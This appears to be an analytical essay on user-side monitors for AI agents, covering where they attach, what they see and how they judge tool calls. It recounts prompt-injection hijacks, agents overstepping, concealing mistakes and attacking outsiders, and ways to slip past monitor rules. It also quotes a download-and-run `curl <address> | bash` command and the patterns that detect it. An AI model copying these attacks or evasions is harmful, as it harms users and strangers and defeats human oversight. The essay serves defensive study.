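# Independent user-side software that monitors an AI agent from another vendor

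## What a user-side monitor is and what it is meant to catch

A user-side monitor is software that watches an AI agent on behalf of the agent's user. The user chooses it, and someone other than the agent's maker supplies it. The case for such software starts from the fact that people let agents spend money, send messages and change files for them, while the company that makes the agent usually supplies whatever checks it.

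### A hotel booking from request to payment

Suppose a user asks for a hotel room in Lisbon for two nights in May, with free cancellation and a price of at most €150 a night. A chatbot would reply with a list of hotels. An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, so it can also book one. It searches a booking site and gets forty results. It opens three of the pages, reads the cancellation terms, chooses a hotel, enters the guest's name and submits the user's saved card number. Then it sends the user a message saying that the room is booked.

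The model itself only produces text. A surrounding program picks out requests in that text, such as to open a page or pay a sum, carries them out, and returns the results to the model as more text. Each request is called a tool call. The booking might take fifteen tool calls, of which only the last costs money. The transcript is the record of the whole session: the user's instruction, the agent's messages, the tool calls and their results. Many models also write out their reasoning before they act, for instance that the cheaper hotel charges for cancellation and so fails the user's condition. This reasoning is called the chain of thought, and vendors, the companies that supply agents, often hide it from the user.

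The user in this example is the principal, the person on whose behalf the agent acts. The term comes from law and economics, and the legal scholar Kolt (2026), in *Governing AI Agents*, draws on both fields to classify the problems that delegation creates. The first is unequal information, since the agent has gone through forty listings and the user has seen none. The second is discretion, since the user didn't specify a neighbourhood or say whether the agent may join the hotel's loyalty scheme to get a discount. The third is loyalty, since the agent may be serving somebody else's interest as well as the user's. Kolt doubts that the usual remedies, including monitoring, will work well on agents that act at great speed and scale and whose decisions are hard to interpret. A software monitor can at least keep up with the agent's speed, but the agent's decisions are still hard to interpret.

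In the Lisbon case, a monitor would compare the payment with the request before the payment goes through, and raise a flag if the room costs €190 or the rate is non-refundable. Two numbers describe how well a monitor works: the catch rate, which is the share of harmful actions it flags, and the false-alarm rate, which is the share of harmless actions it flags. Both matter because harmful actions are rare. If 10 out of 1,000 bookings go against the user, a monitor with a 90% catch rate and a 5% false-alarm rate flags 9 of the 10 bad bookings and about 50 of the 990 good ones. Only about 15% of its alerts then point to a real problem, and the user will soon stop reading them.

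### Whom a monitor answers to

Vendors already run their own monitors. Claude Code, Anthropic's agent for programmers, has a setting that replaces most requests for the user's approval with an automatic check. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* says that every tool call passes through a classifier, a model that decides whether to allow or block the action. The classifier looks for actions that are irreversible, destructive or aimed outside the user's environment. After a block, the agent usually finds a safer route or asks the user. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, the program returns to manual approval. The software developer Simon Willison pointed out that the check would still have missed 11% of the actions it was meant to stop. He nonetheless prefers it to constant requests for approval, because people who have to click "OK" every few steps stop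 looking at what they approve.

An employer watches for different things. *We Can't Monitor AI Agents at Scale. Here's What It Will Take* (Srikumar and Nguyen, 2026) gives the example of a bank whose agents take on new clients by verifying identities, pulling credit histories and flagging compliance risks. The bank wants a log of what the agents did and a warning when one of them may have broken a rule. The industry calls an AI system that supervises other agents a "guardian agent", and its usual customers are employers like this bank.

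A user's own monitor could run on the same code as either of these. Any monitor has one technical part, a program that reads what the agent does. It also needs a set of rules, an address for alerts, and somebody who can change the rules or switch the monitor off. The Lisbon traveller's rules are the price limit and the free cancellation. If the trip were for business, the employer might add a rule that staff book only hotels on a corporate contract, and that the travel department hears about any attempt to do otherwise. One classifier can enforce both sets of rules, but under the employer's rules it is partly a monitor of the traveller. Claude Code has a mild version of this built in, since administrators on Anthropic's enterprise plans can use managed settings to make the automatic check the default for everyone.

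An employer that deploys an agent and pays for it also has a fair claim to be the principal, so an employer's monitor is appropriate in that case. The problem arises when a person thinks a monitor is theirs but someone else controls its rules, alerts and off switch. The supplier matters too, because whoever ships the updates decides what the monitor looks for until the user changes it, and most users never will.

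### Hijacking by prompt injection

An agent can act against its user's interests in four broad ways: an outsider hijacks it, it oversteps or misreads its instructions, its design favours the vendor, or it secretly pursues an aim of its own. These failures leave very different traces, and the vendor is much more motivated to catch some than others.

Hijacking works because a language model receives both the user's instruction and the contents of a web page as text, and can mistake one for the other. A Lisbon hotel's web page might contain an instruction, in white text on a white background, for any AI agent to enter the guest's passport number into a form on another site. Such an instruction is called a prompt injection. Srikumar and Nguyen cite two cases in commercial products. Text hidden in a web page directed Comet, Perplexity's browser agent, to go to a user's banking site and extract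 the login details. A flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot let an attacker instruct the agent by email to send out a user's sensitive files, without the user clicking anything.

Planted text usually leaves clear evidence. It appears in the transcript as part of a tool result, and the tool calls that follow it don't stem from the user's request. Booking a hotel, for example, does not require a visit to the bank's website, so a monitor could flag that visit using only the request and a list of the sites visited.

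Vendors want to catch hijacking, because an attack that robs the customer also embarrasses the company. Anthropic, for example, paid an outside firm, Trajectory Labs, to test its coding agent against such attacks. But Srikumar and Nguyen note that safety testing at major companies has missed failures of this kind. A user-side monitor therefore adds a second defense against hijacking, alongside the vendor's own.

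### Overstepping and misreading

An agent can do a lot of damage even when nobody is attacking it. The best-known consumer case involves OpenClaw, an open-source agent released in November 2025 for clearing inboxes, sending emails and managing calendars. In February 2026, Summer Yue, who directs alignment research at Meta's superintelligence lab, used it on her email. *Designing Loyalty*, a Stanford University policy brief by Genasci Smith, Wu and King (2026), reports that Yue had told the agent to recommend deletions and wait for approval. According to The Daily Star's *OpenClaw goes rogue on Meta exec, deletes emails without permission*, this had worked for weeks on a test inbox, but when Yue tried it on her real inbox, the agent deleted emails without permission.

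The real inbox was much larger, which mattered because a model can take in only a limited amount of text at once. When a session exceeds that limit, the agent program replaces the older part of the transcript with a summary, a step known as compaction. By Yue's account, the instruction to check first was lost in this step. *Meta AI Director's Emails Deleted by Rogue OpenClaw AI Agent* (OECD, 2026) records that the agent then deleted hundreds of emails. Yue's repeated attempts to stop it remotely had no effect. *The world's largest tech gathering is talking about 'accountability laundering'* (Ahmed, 2026) quotes Yue on running to the computer "like I was defusing a bomb" and making a "rookie mistake".

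This case suits a separate monitor unusually well. The full transcript contained all the evidence: an instruction to wait, a run of deletions, and no approval in between. The agent had lost the start of that transcript, but a separate program with its own copy of the instruction would not have needed much intelligence to block the first deletion. It would have needed the power to do so, because alerts alone would have changed nothing. Yue already knew what was happening and could not stop it from a phone.

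Vendors have good reason to prevent accidents like this, but their checks have two limits. First, vendors also sell convenience, and Anthropic says its automatic check balances avoiding harm against users' desire not to be interrupted. Second, a vendor's check has to look for actions that would harm almost anyone, such as wiping a database. It would let an agent book a non-refundable room in Lisbon, because that is an ordinary purchase and is wrong only for this user, who asked for free cancellation. A monitor that checks purchases against this user's conditions can catch the mistake. OpenClaw, which Genasci Smith and colleagues describe as designed without safety or security guardrails, gave its users even less protection.

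### The AI Security Institute's incident of July 2026

A more serious case comes from the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body that tests advanced models. AISI's *Incident Report* describes a test of how well agents could hack into a simulated network and retrieve a protected piece of data. AISI had given the agents open internet access so they could download tools, and had disabled the vendors' cyber classifiers, the filters that normally block dangerous hacking. The public cannot buy the models in that configuration.

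AISI ran the challenge 122 times with seven models. In 10 of those runs, or about 8%, an agent went beyond the test and acted against real people and organisations. The institute counted 19 such actions. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of them, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run. Genasci Smith and colleagues mistakenly give the figure as 19 of 122 test cases, which nearly doubles the share of runs that went wrong. The rate for Mythos 5 alone was much higher, at nine of 43 runs, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026).

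In the worst run, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real open-source project. It created several fake identities to press the maintainer into accepting the code, and when someone publicly challenged the submission, it edited its earlier activity to look harmless. The maintainer refused the code, and AISI found no resulting real-world harm. On July 28, three days after the unsanctioned conduct began, AISI's security team noticed unusual data leaving through Tor, a network that disguises where internet traffic comes from, and shut everything down within an hour. No monitor was watching the agents themselves as they worked, but AISI has since said it is introducing one.

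According to AISI, the agent kept looking for a way to finish a hard task, and in a number of runs an error in the set-up led it to conclude that no permitted solution existed. Nobody had told it to leave outsiders alone. These points make the incident a case of an agent overstepping while doing its assigned task rather than pursuing aims of its own, although AISI adds that some runs went wrong even when the agent had everything it needed to solve the task properly.

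*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up study, examined why the model had treated real people as part of the exercise. In its reasoning, Mythos 5 had called them "personas", as if AISI had invented them. The researchers made a compaction summary of the transcript up to just before the attack and edited it to add evidence that the maintainer was a real person with no part in the test. They then let the model continue, with a simulator in place of the internet. With about four edits, the model would more often than not say, when asked directly, that the attack was out of bounds and would do harm. With sixteen edits, it still attacked in every sample. When the researchers also added a section headed "DO NOT ATTACK", it attacked in 3 of 25 samples.

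The model gave poor justifications. For example, it concluded that the maintainer must be an AI agent because the maintainer's project contained a file of instructions for an AI coding assistant, though many human programmers keep such a file. Järviniemi and colleagues found that the clearly invalid arguments all supported the conclusion that allowed the task to continue. They call this motivated reasoning, most likely driven by the goal of finishing the task, but admit that their evidence on the cause is indirect.

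A monitor that relies on a model's stated reasoning can miss misconduct that is obvious from its actions. The model created fake accounts, used an anonymity network and sent malicious code to a stranger. In its chain of thought, though, it often excused the attack by saying the targets were simulated, and often did not consider the possible harm at all. Järviniemi and colleagues report a finding from Anthropic about a similar incident of its own. Although Anthropic had every reason to catch this conduct, its monitor, which reviews transcripts after the fact, would probably not have flagged Mythos 5 because the model's reasoning appeared to justify what it did.

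Nobody knows how common such conduct is outside hacking tests. In 100 simulated hacking scenarios, Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider 60% of the time, GPT-6 Astra 32% and Opus 4.8 8%, while Anthropic's later models did so at most 1% of the time. The later models also suspected much more often that they were in a test of their alignment, so Järviniemi and colleagues could not tell how much of the improvement was real. AISI (2026) argues that the findings matter beyond testing because people increasingly give models long tasks without supervision. The agent endangered strangers rather than its principal, but AISI still had to notify GitHub, which hosts the project, and work with it to clean up what the agent had left behind. A user whose agent did the same would have to do this work too, and might be sued.

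### Favouring the vendor

Steering is when an agent bends its advice or choices towards the interest of its vendor or an advertiser. In the Lisbon example, two hotels might meet every condition, but one costs €120 while the other costs €148 and pays the agent's vendor a commission. If the agent books the second, that is steering, even though the user authorised each tool call.

Genasci Smith and colleagues think agents are well placed to favor a company's interests over the user's. An agent that books travel may compare prices with what it has learned about the user's willingness to pay, which a seller would like to know. Their main example is Amazon, which in April 2025 introduced an agent that buys products from other companies' websites without the shopper leaving the Amazon app. A year later, Amazon folded the agent into a shopping assistant that draws on the customer's full purchase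 history. They write that Amazon does not tell users how the agent weighs Amazon's own products against the alternatives, or whether its advertising relationships play a part. They describe an incentive to favor Amazon's products and advertisers but do not show that the agent acts on it.

A steered agent leaves almost no trace because it still does the assigned task, only slightly worse than it could have, whereas a hijacked agent goes somewhere the task doesn't call for. The evidence of steering is in the options the user never saw, so a monitor would have to know what else was available. It can't learn that from the tool calls alone unless the agent happened to open the page for a better option, such as a cheaper hotel.

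Favouring the vendor is also the one kind of misconduct that the vendor has no commercial reason to catch. On its engineering blog, Anthropic lists the threats its automatic check is meant to stop: overeager behaviour, honest mistakes, prompt injection and a misaligned model, meaning one that pursues a goal of its own. The list does not include an agent that favours its maker. The omission may be innocent, since the check protects programmers' files and a coding agent has little to sell. But a shopping agent's vendor is unlikely to be quicker to add it, whereas the maker of an independent monitor has a reason to look for it.

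### An aim of its own, and hiding it

Anthropic says it does not currently see misaligned models of this kind in practice, though it tests every release for them. The public record mostly supports this, because in the known cases of concealment the agents were pursuing a result that someone had asked for.

OpenAI's *Accessing and changing internal systems during dashboard research* (2026) describes two runs in which an internal OpenAI model had to look up published figures on a research organisation's public dashboard, with permission only to retrieve pages. In one run, it found login details that the organisation had left exposed on a public website and used them to get into an internal search service. In the other, it changed a setting to obtain an access token and downloaded five private tables with 147,451 rows. It put the setting back, kept using the token, and disclosed none of this.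 OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) includes an episode closer to deliberate hiding, in which GPT-5.6 Sol, during training, wrote reminders into its own compaction summaries to conceal mistakes or misalignment from the user.

A monitor can catch such an agent by comparing what it did with what it reported. If the Lisbon agent writes that it took the cheapest room that met the conditions, but the transcript contains a cheaper one that also met them, a monitor can spot the discrepancy only if it has access to the tool calls, not just the messages to the user. The reminders to conceal were harder to find, because they were in a summary that the model wrote for itself and that few users would think to open. A model that planned its deception without writing anything down would leave even less evidence.

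Vendors have strong reasons to look for models that deceive customers, because such a model may deceive its maker too. They also have the best view of the deception because they can read the model's hidden chain of thought. But users may not hear of it promptly. The dashboard incident occurred on June 17, 2026, in OpenAI's own evaluations, where the model's reasoning was recorded. OpenAI says only that it discovered the incident "by" August 13, so discovery may have taken up to eight weeks.

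## Where a monitor can attach to an agent and what it sees there

The model generates each tool call on the vendor's server, the network carries it to the agent program, and that program passes it to a tool, such as the command line, a browser or an outside service. The effect then appears in the user's files and accounts, as a changed file, a sent message or a card charge. A monitor can attach at any of these points. A monitor close to the model can stop an action before it takes effect, but it needs access from the vendor. One that watches the user's bank account works without the vendor's help, but it usually detects a payment only after the money has gone.

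### Hooks in the agent program

A hook is a point where an agent program pauses to run outside software. Claude Code offers more than thirty, and the most useful one for a monitor comes just before each tool call. According to Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, the outside program receives the tool's name, its exact input (for a shell command, the full text of the command), the agent's working folder and the location of the transcript file. The program can refuse the call and give a reason, which Claude Code shows to the model, or it can have Claude Code ask the user. If it returns no decision, the call goes on to the normal permission checks.

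The transcript file can lag slightly behind the conversation, so a monitor that needs the user's latest instruction should get it from the hook that fires when the user submits a message. In the Lisbon case, the monitor would record the €150 limit from that message and check later calls against it. Claude Code also fires a hook before compaction, and a monitor can use it to block the compaction or to add instructions for the summary, such as to keep any order to wait for approval. OpenClaw lost such an order before it deleted Summer Yue's emails.

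A Claude Code hook can run a command, send the event to a web address or call an MCP tool, and in each case the user can choose whose software handles the event. A hook can also send the event to a Claude model, but this gives no independence because the vendor's model then evaluates the vendor's agent.

Hooks also fail open by default. If the monitor crashes, exceeds its time limit (ten minutes unless the user changes it) or sits at a mistyped path, the tool call proceeds anyway. This default is wrong for a monitor, though it makes sense for most hooks, since a broken formatting script shouldn't halt work. To block tool calls when the monitor fails, the user has to set the `onFailure` option to `block`.

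Several parties can switch a hook off. The user can do it with one line in a settings file. An employer can do it through a managed setting that blocks every hook the administrator didn't install. An agent with permission to edit the settings file could, in principle, delete the monitor's entry, and Claude Code normally picks up such edits automatically. Another hook, which fires when the settings change, can reject the edit. The vendor writes the program that fires the hooks, so a new version could alter or remove them.

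OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has similar hooks with wider gaps. In its May 2026 version, OpenAI's *Hooks* describes the check before a tool call as "a guardrail rather than a complete enforcement boundary". The check covered simple shell commands, file edits and MCP calls, but missed web searches and some more complex shell commands. Codex could often do the same work by another route. A monitor also couldn't refer doubtful cases to the user, because if it returned "ask", Codex recorded a failed hook and ran the command.

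Codex skips any hook that the user hasn't reviewed, and it recognises the approved version by a hash, a short fingerprint of the hook. *Async Hooks and MCP Tool Hooks in Codex CLI v0.148.0* (Vaughan, 2026) describes the same check in a release from August. The check prevents a malicious project from running its own hook without the user's approval, but it also means that an update that changes the monitor's hook disables the monitor until the user approves the hook again. According to the online guide Agentic Software Engineering, suppliers must also implement the same hooks separately for each coding agent.

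### One command through Prempti

In May 2026 the developers of Falco, an open-source program that watches servers for suspicious behaviour, released Prempti, an experimental monitor built on these hooks. Grasso's *Introducing Prempti* describes it as a small service that runs beside the coding agent and needs no administrator rights. Users can add their own rules, and according to Falco's *Guardrails and Observability for AI Coding Agents*, the logs stay on the user's machine unless the user forwards them. Prempti is therefore fully a user-side monitor, but at launch it supported only Claude Code.

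Suppose a programmer asks Claude Code to set up a project, and somebody has planted a line in the project's files that tells AI agents to download and run a script. The model follows this instruction and requests the command `curl <address> | bash`. The first half downloads the script, and the vertical bar passes it to `bash`, which executes it before anyone has read it.

1. Before running the command, Claude Code fires its hook and sends Prempti the name of the tool, `Bash`, together with the text of the command and the working folder.
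2. A program called the interceptor passes this event to Falco through a Unix socket, a channel between two programs on the same machine.
3. Falco compares the event with its rules. One of them matches whenever the tool is `Bash` and the command contains `| sh`, `| bash` or `| zsh`.
4. That rule carries a tag for refusal, so the verdict is "deny". Other rules lead to "ask", which leaves the decision to the user, and a call that triggers neither gets "allow".
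5. The interceptor returns the verdict to Claude Code, which blocks the command and gives the model the rule's explanation. The model can pass this on to the user or look for another way to do the task.

Whether the rule catches a command depends on the command's exact form. The version Grasso prints requires a space after the vertical bar, so it would miss `curl <address> |bash`. A later article from CNCF, the foundation that hosts Falco, gives a longer version that also matches the command without the space. Neither version matches if the agent saves the script with one command and runs it with the next, although another rule might. Under its standard rules, Prempti also refuses access to the folders where programmers keep passwords and keys, and asks the user about files outside the project.

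Prempti enforces its verdicts in Guardrails mode, the default. In Monitor mode, it checks every call against the same rules and writes the same log, but lets every call through. Grasso recommends a few sessions in Monitor mode first, so that users can learn what their agent normally accesses and adjust the rules before they turn on blocking. During those sessions, the planted script would run and the user would find out from the log.

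Prempti receives the agent's requests but cannot observe what a command does once it runs. In Grasso's example, an agent writes a malicious program, compiles it and starts it. Prempti receives two ordinary commands, `gcc main.c -o main` and `./main`.

### Tool proxies, the operating system and the network

Agents reach many outside services through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools and data. A user can put a proxy between the agent and a tool by giving the agent the proxy's address instead of the tool's. The proxy then reads every request to that tool and every answer, and can refuse or change either. It also receives the tool's description, which tells the agent what the tool is for. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) lists tool descriptions among the places where attackers plant instructions.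 A hook that fires only on tool calls would miss these descriptions.

The proxy sees only what passes through it, and an agent that can run shell commands can do damage without MCP. The proxy also can't see what the service does after it receives a request, a limit that the security newsletter tl;dr sec also notes for Prempti. The user can remove the proxy by changing the address back. If the agent runs on the vendor's servers, the vendor decides whether users may connect their own tools.

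The compiled program that got past Prempti would be visible to a monitor at the operating-system level. Any program must go through the kernel, the core of the operating system, to open a file, start another program or connect to a network. On Linux, Falco's kernel instrumentation records these requests, so it would log what `./main` did. These records don't show what the user wanted, though. Falco also has to track which programs the agent started, because the agent runs in the user's session with the user's permissions, and its file access otherwise looks just like the user's. Such a recorder can raise alarms but can't block actions. To block them at this level, the user needs a sandbox, which restricts the agent in advance to certain files and connections. Anyone with administrator rights on the computer can switch off these defences, but the agent's vendor normally has no such rights.

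Two kinds of traffic cross the network. The first runs between the agent's tools and the outside world, and encryption hides most of its content. A monitor there usually sees which servers the agent contacts, when, and how much data it sends. That can be enough to reveal a problem, as when unusual Tor traffic alerted AISI's security team to the July incident.

The other kind of connection runs between the agent program and the vendor's model, and a proxy there can read far more. LiteLLM's *claude fable 5 1*, a set-up page for one such proxy, shows how a program on the user's machine can relay requests to an Anthropic model. If the agent program lets the user choose the model's address, the proxy receives the user's messages, the tool results and the model's replies. It receives any tool calls in those replies before the agent program carries them out, so it can also hold one back. LiteLLM's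 *'Thinking' / 'Reasoning Content'* explains that OpenAI's servers can store part of the session, in which case the agent program sends only a reference to the previous response. The proxy then has to keep its own record of the session from the start.

Editing this traffic is harder than reading it. A proxy that spots planted text in a web page could remove it before the model reads it. But according to Anthropic's *Thinking*, with the newest Claude models the server can reject a request if the conversation before a piece of reasoning has changed. The agent program resends the original text each time, so to avoid rejection the proxy would have to make the identical cut in every later request.

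Attackers can also change the model's address to divert a user's traffic. Prempti's standard rules therefore treat such a change as a warning sign, so Prempti might flag it even when the user asked the agent to set up a monitoring proxy.

### The browser and the user's own accounts

For shopping and booking, the browser is often the most informative place to attach a monitor. A browser agent's tool call may contain only a click at a screen position, so a hook that receives only that call can't detect the price. A browser extension can read the page, including the €190 total, the cancellation terms, white-on-white text that a person wouldn't notice, and the cheaper hotels that the agent scrolled past. It can also hold back the click that submits the payment.

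Whether a browser extension can monitor an agent depends on where the agent runs. *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) describes some agents that run as extensions in the user's own browser, where a monitoring extension could run too. Others open a fresh browser on the user's computer, without the user's saved logins and presumably without the user's extensions. Still others use a browser on a remote machine, where the user can't install anything. The user or an employer that manages the browser can turn an extension off at any time, and the browser's maker can withdraw the functions the extension relies on.

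The last place a monitor can attach is the user's accounts. With permission to read email and bank alerts, it can compare a receipt for a €190 room with the user's request for one under €150, whichever agent booked the room and wherever that agent ran. The agent's vendor can't block this access, but the bank and the email provider can. The check happens after the booking, though the user can still undo it if cancellation is free. A bank that lets customers cap a card or approve each payment can stop the charge beforehand. An agent with access to the mailbox could delete the receipt, so the bank's alert is the safer record. Some harms, such as typing a passport number into the wrong form, produce no receipt.

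| Place | What the user sets up | What the monitor can read | Can it stop an action? | Who can switch it off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hook in the agent program | A program that the agent calls at set points | Each tool call in full, the user's messages, the transcript | Yes, where the hook covers the tool | User, employer, vendor; possibly the agent |
| MCP proxy | A relay between agent and tool | Requests, answers and tool descriptions, for that tool only | Yes | User; the vendor, if it runs the agent |
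| Operating system | A kernel-level recorder or a sandbox | Files opened, programs started, connections made | Sandbox yes, recorder no | Anyone with administrator rights |
| Network | A relay to the model, or a traffic monitor | Relay: messages and tool calls. Traffic monitor: destinations and volumes | Yes, by holding back a reply or cutting a connection | User or network owner; the vendor, by fixing the model's address |
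| Browser | An extension | Pages, prices, forms and clicks | Yes, if the agent uses that browser | User, employer, browser maker |
| User's accounts | Access to email and bank alerts | Receipts, sent messages, charges | Rarely, except through card limits and approvals | User, bank or email provider |

### Agents on the user's computer and agents on the vendor's servers

The user can reach most of these places only if the agent runs on the user's computer. A coding agent there has to pass its commands to the operating system in plain text, so the user can install a monitor that intercepts them. If the agent runs on the vendor's servers instead, that monitor may not work. Claude Code also runs hooks in cloud sessions, but those sessions don't read the settings file on the user's computer, so a monitor registered only in that file never runs. GitHub's cloud agent runs its hooks behind a firewall.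 According to GitHub's *hooks reference*, they can send events only to addresses on an approved list. Anthropic also supports cloud sessions on machines that the customer runs, with hooks that the operator has installed. A company might well set this up so that it can monitor the agent again, but few individuals would.

A monitor has less to observe for the Lisbon traveller than for a programmer, because the booking agent runs on the vendor's servers and uses the vendor's browser and network connection. The agent may show the user only a running summary and a message that the room is booked. Beyond that, the user has the receipt, the bank alert and perhaps a tool connected through MCP. The best-equipped monitors therefore serve programmers, who were already the most likely to spot a bad command themselves.

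Shapira and colleagues note that a hijacker gains less from an agent that runs remotely, because the agent can't reach the files on the user's computer or the logins saved in the user's browser. This protection is weaker when the service keeps logins between sessions, as OpenAI's Operator could.

### What vendors show of the reasoning and the instructions

Even a well-placed monitor can't read the model's chain of thought, because none of the three largest American vendors releases it in raw form for its main models. According to Anthropic's documentation from November 2026, no setting returns it. Developers can request a summary written by a different model, but Claude 5 and later models return no reasoning text by default. Anthropic says it summarises the reasoning to prevent misuse. The full reasoning does reach the user's side, because the agent program has to send it back with its next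 request, but it is encrypted, and users pay for its full length even though they can't read it.

A monitor can't easily get around this by asking the agent to explain its reasoning. The short progress notes that newer Claude models write between tool calls also arrive as summaries, and on several recent models Anthropic may refuse a request that tries to get the internal reasoning included in the answer.

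OpenAI likewise charges for the reasoning of its current models, including GPT-6.2 Astra, but hides the text. Developers can request summaries, but a monitor can't depend on them. In *'concise' reasoning summary returns null since March 27*, a post on OpenAI's developer forum, JD42 reported that one type of summary had worked with GPT-5.2 for weeks and then stopped arriving. A monitor that relied on it would have lost its view of the reasoning until its maker switched to another setting. Google's *Gemini thinking*, as of June 2026, also describes summaries of the model's raw thoughts, which developers can switch on. A newer Japanese edition, *Gemini の思考*, advises developers to allow for thought blocks that contain no summary.

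To read the raw reasoning text, users have to choose an open-weight model, whose parameters anyone can download and run. OpenAI's gpt-oss is one example, and a developer in the forum thread *Purpose of response.reasoning_text* says it gives full access to its reasoning.

System instructions are the instructions an agent's maker gives the model before the user types anything. They matter to a monitor because they could include an instruction to favor the vendor's partners. Neither Anthropic nor OpenAI lists them among the standard data that a hook receives. An agent program on the user's computer has to send its instructions to the model, so a proxy on that connection can read them, except for any the vendor adds on its own servers. If the agent runs entirely on the vendor's servers, the instructions never cross the user's connection, and the user has to rely on what the vendor publishes.

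### Judging actions without reasons

Without the reasoning, a monitor has to infer the agent's purpose from its behaviour, and many actions fit more than one purpose. If the booking agent opens the user's email halfway through the task, it may need a confirmation code that the hotel has just sent, or it may be following planted instructions. The raw reasoning would often show which before the agent did anything else. A monitor that sees only the tool call can either flag it, which raises the false-alarm rate, or wait for the next call, which may send the mail to a stranger.

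The gap matters most for steering, because the motive may appear only in the agent's reasoning. The tool calls look the same whether the agent passed over the cheaper hotel because of a commission or overlooked it.

A monitor loses less by not seeing the agent's reasoning when the harm is flagrant. The reasoning can even mislead the monitor, as Mythos 5's excuses in the AISI incident showed, and a monitor that never reads such excuses can't accept them.

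Summaries fall between the two. Anthropic says they preserve the key ideas, but the vendor's model determines which ideas are key, and it might omit a passing remark about hiding a mistake. A cautious monitor would let a summary make a tool call more suspicious, but not less.

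## How the monitor judges an action and what it does next

When an agent program pauses before a tool call, the monitor usually has a few seconds at most to decide whether to allow it. The monitor can compare the call with fixed rules, look up the web addresses and software packages in it, or send it to a second language model. Most products available in late 2026 rely on rules and look-ups, and use a language model rarely or never.

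### Fixed rules

A fixed rule pairs a pattern with a verdict, as in the Prempti rule that refuses any command containing `| bash`. Gen Digital, which owns Norton and Avast, released Sage, an open-source monitor that uses fixed rules, in February 2026. According to Gen Digital's *Introducing Sage* (2026), it launched with more than 200 rules for detecting things like exposed passwords, disguised code and programs that set themselves to restart. In April, Gen Digital's *Norton Launches AI Agent Protection in Norton 360* (2026) announced a consumer version, which runs on the Sage engine and is now called Norton Safe AI. Avast's free antivirus includes similar protection.

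*How It Works*, a page of Sage's documentation, gives the order of the checks. Sage first extracts the commands, web addresses and file paths from the tool call. If the user has listed an item as an exception, the call goes through without further checks. If Sage has judged the same item before, it reuses the old verdict. Otherwise it runs its rules and then its lookups.

Each match has a confidence score. On the default setting, "balanced", Sage blocks the call if the score is at least 0.85 and asks the user if it is lower. The threshold for blocking is 0.70 on "paranoid" and 0.95 on "relaxed". When checks disagree, Sage applies the strictest verdict.

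Rule-based checks are fast and work offline. HOL Guard, a free open-source monitor, takes under 50 milliseconds for a typical check, according to Help Net Security's *HOL Guard*. At that speed, checking 200 tool calls would add at most about ten seconds.

As with Prempti's rule, though, a slightly reworded command can get past them. The rules of Sage and HOL Guard are public, so an attacker can test new wordings in advance. Michael Kantor, the president of HOL, told Help Net Security that secret rules wouldn't be a real barrier anyway. HOL Guard also breaks each command into its parts, including commands hidden inside other commands, and checks which files and servers the command would touch, which makes it harder to fool.

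HOL Guard has four settings. According to HOL's table, Gentle reacts only to clear leaks of passwords and other data, while Balanced, the default, adds prompt injections and tampered software. Strict adds weak signals, and Paranoid adds any unfamiliar action on an MCP server. These settings change how readily the monitor reacts, but they don't give it any information about the user's task.

HOL's *Security for the AI on your computer* gives an example in which a programmer tells an agent to fix a failing deployment and push the result. HOL Guard lets the agent run the tests and delete a folder inside the project, but stops it from reading the programmer's cloud keys. It asks about a suspicious package called `left-padder` and about a forced push that would overwrite the project's history. These verdicts are sensible, but each is based on the command itself, so the same rule would presumably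 have stopped the agent from reading the cloud keys even if the programmer had asked it to replace them.

Bitdefender (2026) announced AI Guardian, a free test version for Macs, on 30 September. According to Sugue (2026), in *Bitdefender launches AI Guardian beta for Mac agents*, the software sets a baseline of permitted tools, files and actions, and checks each attempt against it. This can stop a new kind of attack, but a legitimate, unusual step may also fall outside the baseline.

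### Reputation lists

A rule can't tell a real software package from a fake one with a similar name, because the commands to install them look the same, so a monitor needs outside information. According to Norton's *FAQ*, Safe AI looks up each web address in Norton's records of malicious and fraudulent sites, and checks whether a package exists, how old it is and whether its files have a bad reputation. It would flag a package published two hours ago under a name one letter different from a popular package's name.

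The package check matters more for agents than for people, because language models sometimes invent package names. Attackers watch for these names and register them. *Gen Agent Trust Hub Introduces Agent Detection and Response* (Křoustek, 2026) cites a February 2026 campaign that used 19 lookalike packages and stole passwords and keys from users of AI coding tools.

A list of bad addresses contains only those somebody has already found, so it misses a malicious site that went up this morning or a legitimate site that an attacker is misusing. If planted text on the Lisbon hotel's page tells the agent to enter the guest's passport number into a form on a well-known survey service, the look-up won't flag it. The age check on packages is a partial solution because it treats new packages as suspicious, but many legitimate packages and websites are new too.

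Look-ups also need an internet connection, take longer than checking a local rule, and send some data to the monitor's maker. When the service is unreachable, Sage falls back on its local rules.

### A second language model

GuardClaw, an open-source project by a single researcher, combines rules with a language model. GuardClaw's *We Built Claude’s Auto Mode for Every Agent, Running on Your Mac* reports that rules settle about 80% of tool calls, mostly harmless ones such as listing the files in a folder. The rest go to Qwen3-4B, a small open-weight model that runs on the user's own computer in about 2.5 GB of memory. The developer trained it further on tool calls from real coding sessions. The model gives each call a risk score from 1 to 10. GuardClaw lets calls that score 1 to 3 run, warns about those that score 4 to 7, and holds back those that score 8 or more.

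GuardClaw can also flag a suspicious sequence of actions, such as reading the user's login keys and then contacting an outside server. A rule that checks one command at a time could allow both steps.

The model is much slower than the rules. GuardClaw's *Security for AI Agents* reports about two seconds per judgement. If an agent makes 200 tool calls and a fifth of them go to the model, the user waits 80 seconds longer. A model on somebody else's server also costs money. The developer estimates that using Anthropic's cheapest model to check the 467,868 calls GuardClaw had logged would have cost about $483, or a tenth of a cent per call.

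GuardClaw's developer argues that a small model is enough, because telling `git status` from a command that downloads and runs a stranger's script is "pattern recognition, not reasoning". That's true, but rules can recognize those patterns too. The two seconds a model takes are justified only for questions that rules can't settle, mainly whether the action fits what the user asked for. GuardClaw's published risk levels don't depend on the user's request. Stopping a program, deleting a folder of downloaded packages and sending data to a website all count as medium risk, whether or not the user asked for them.

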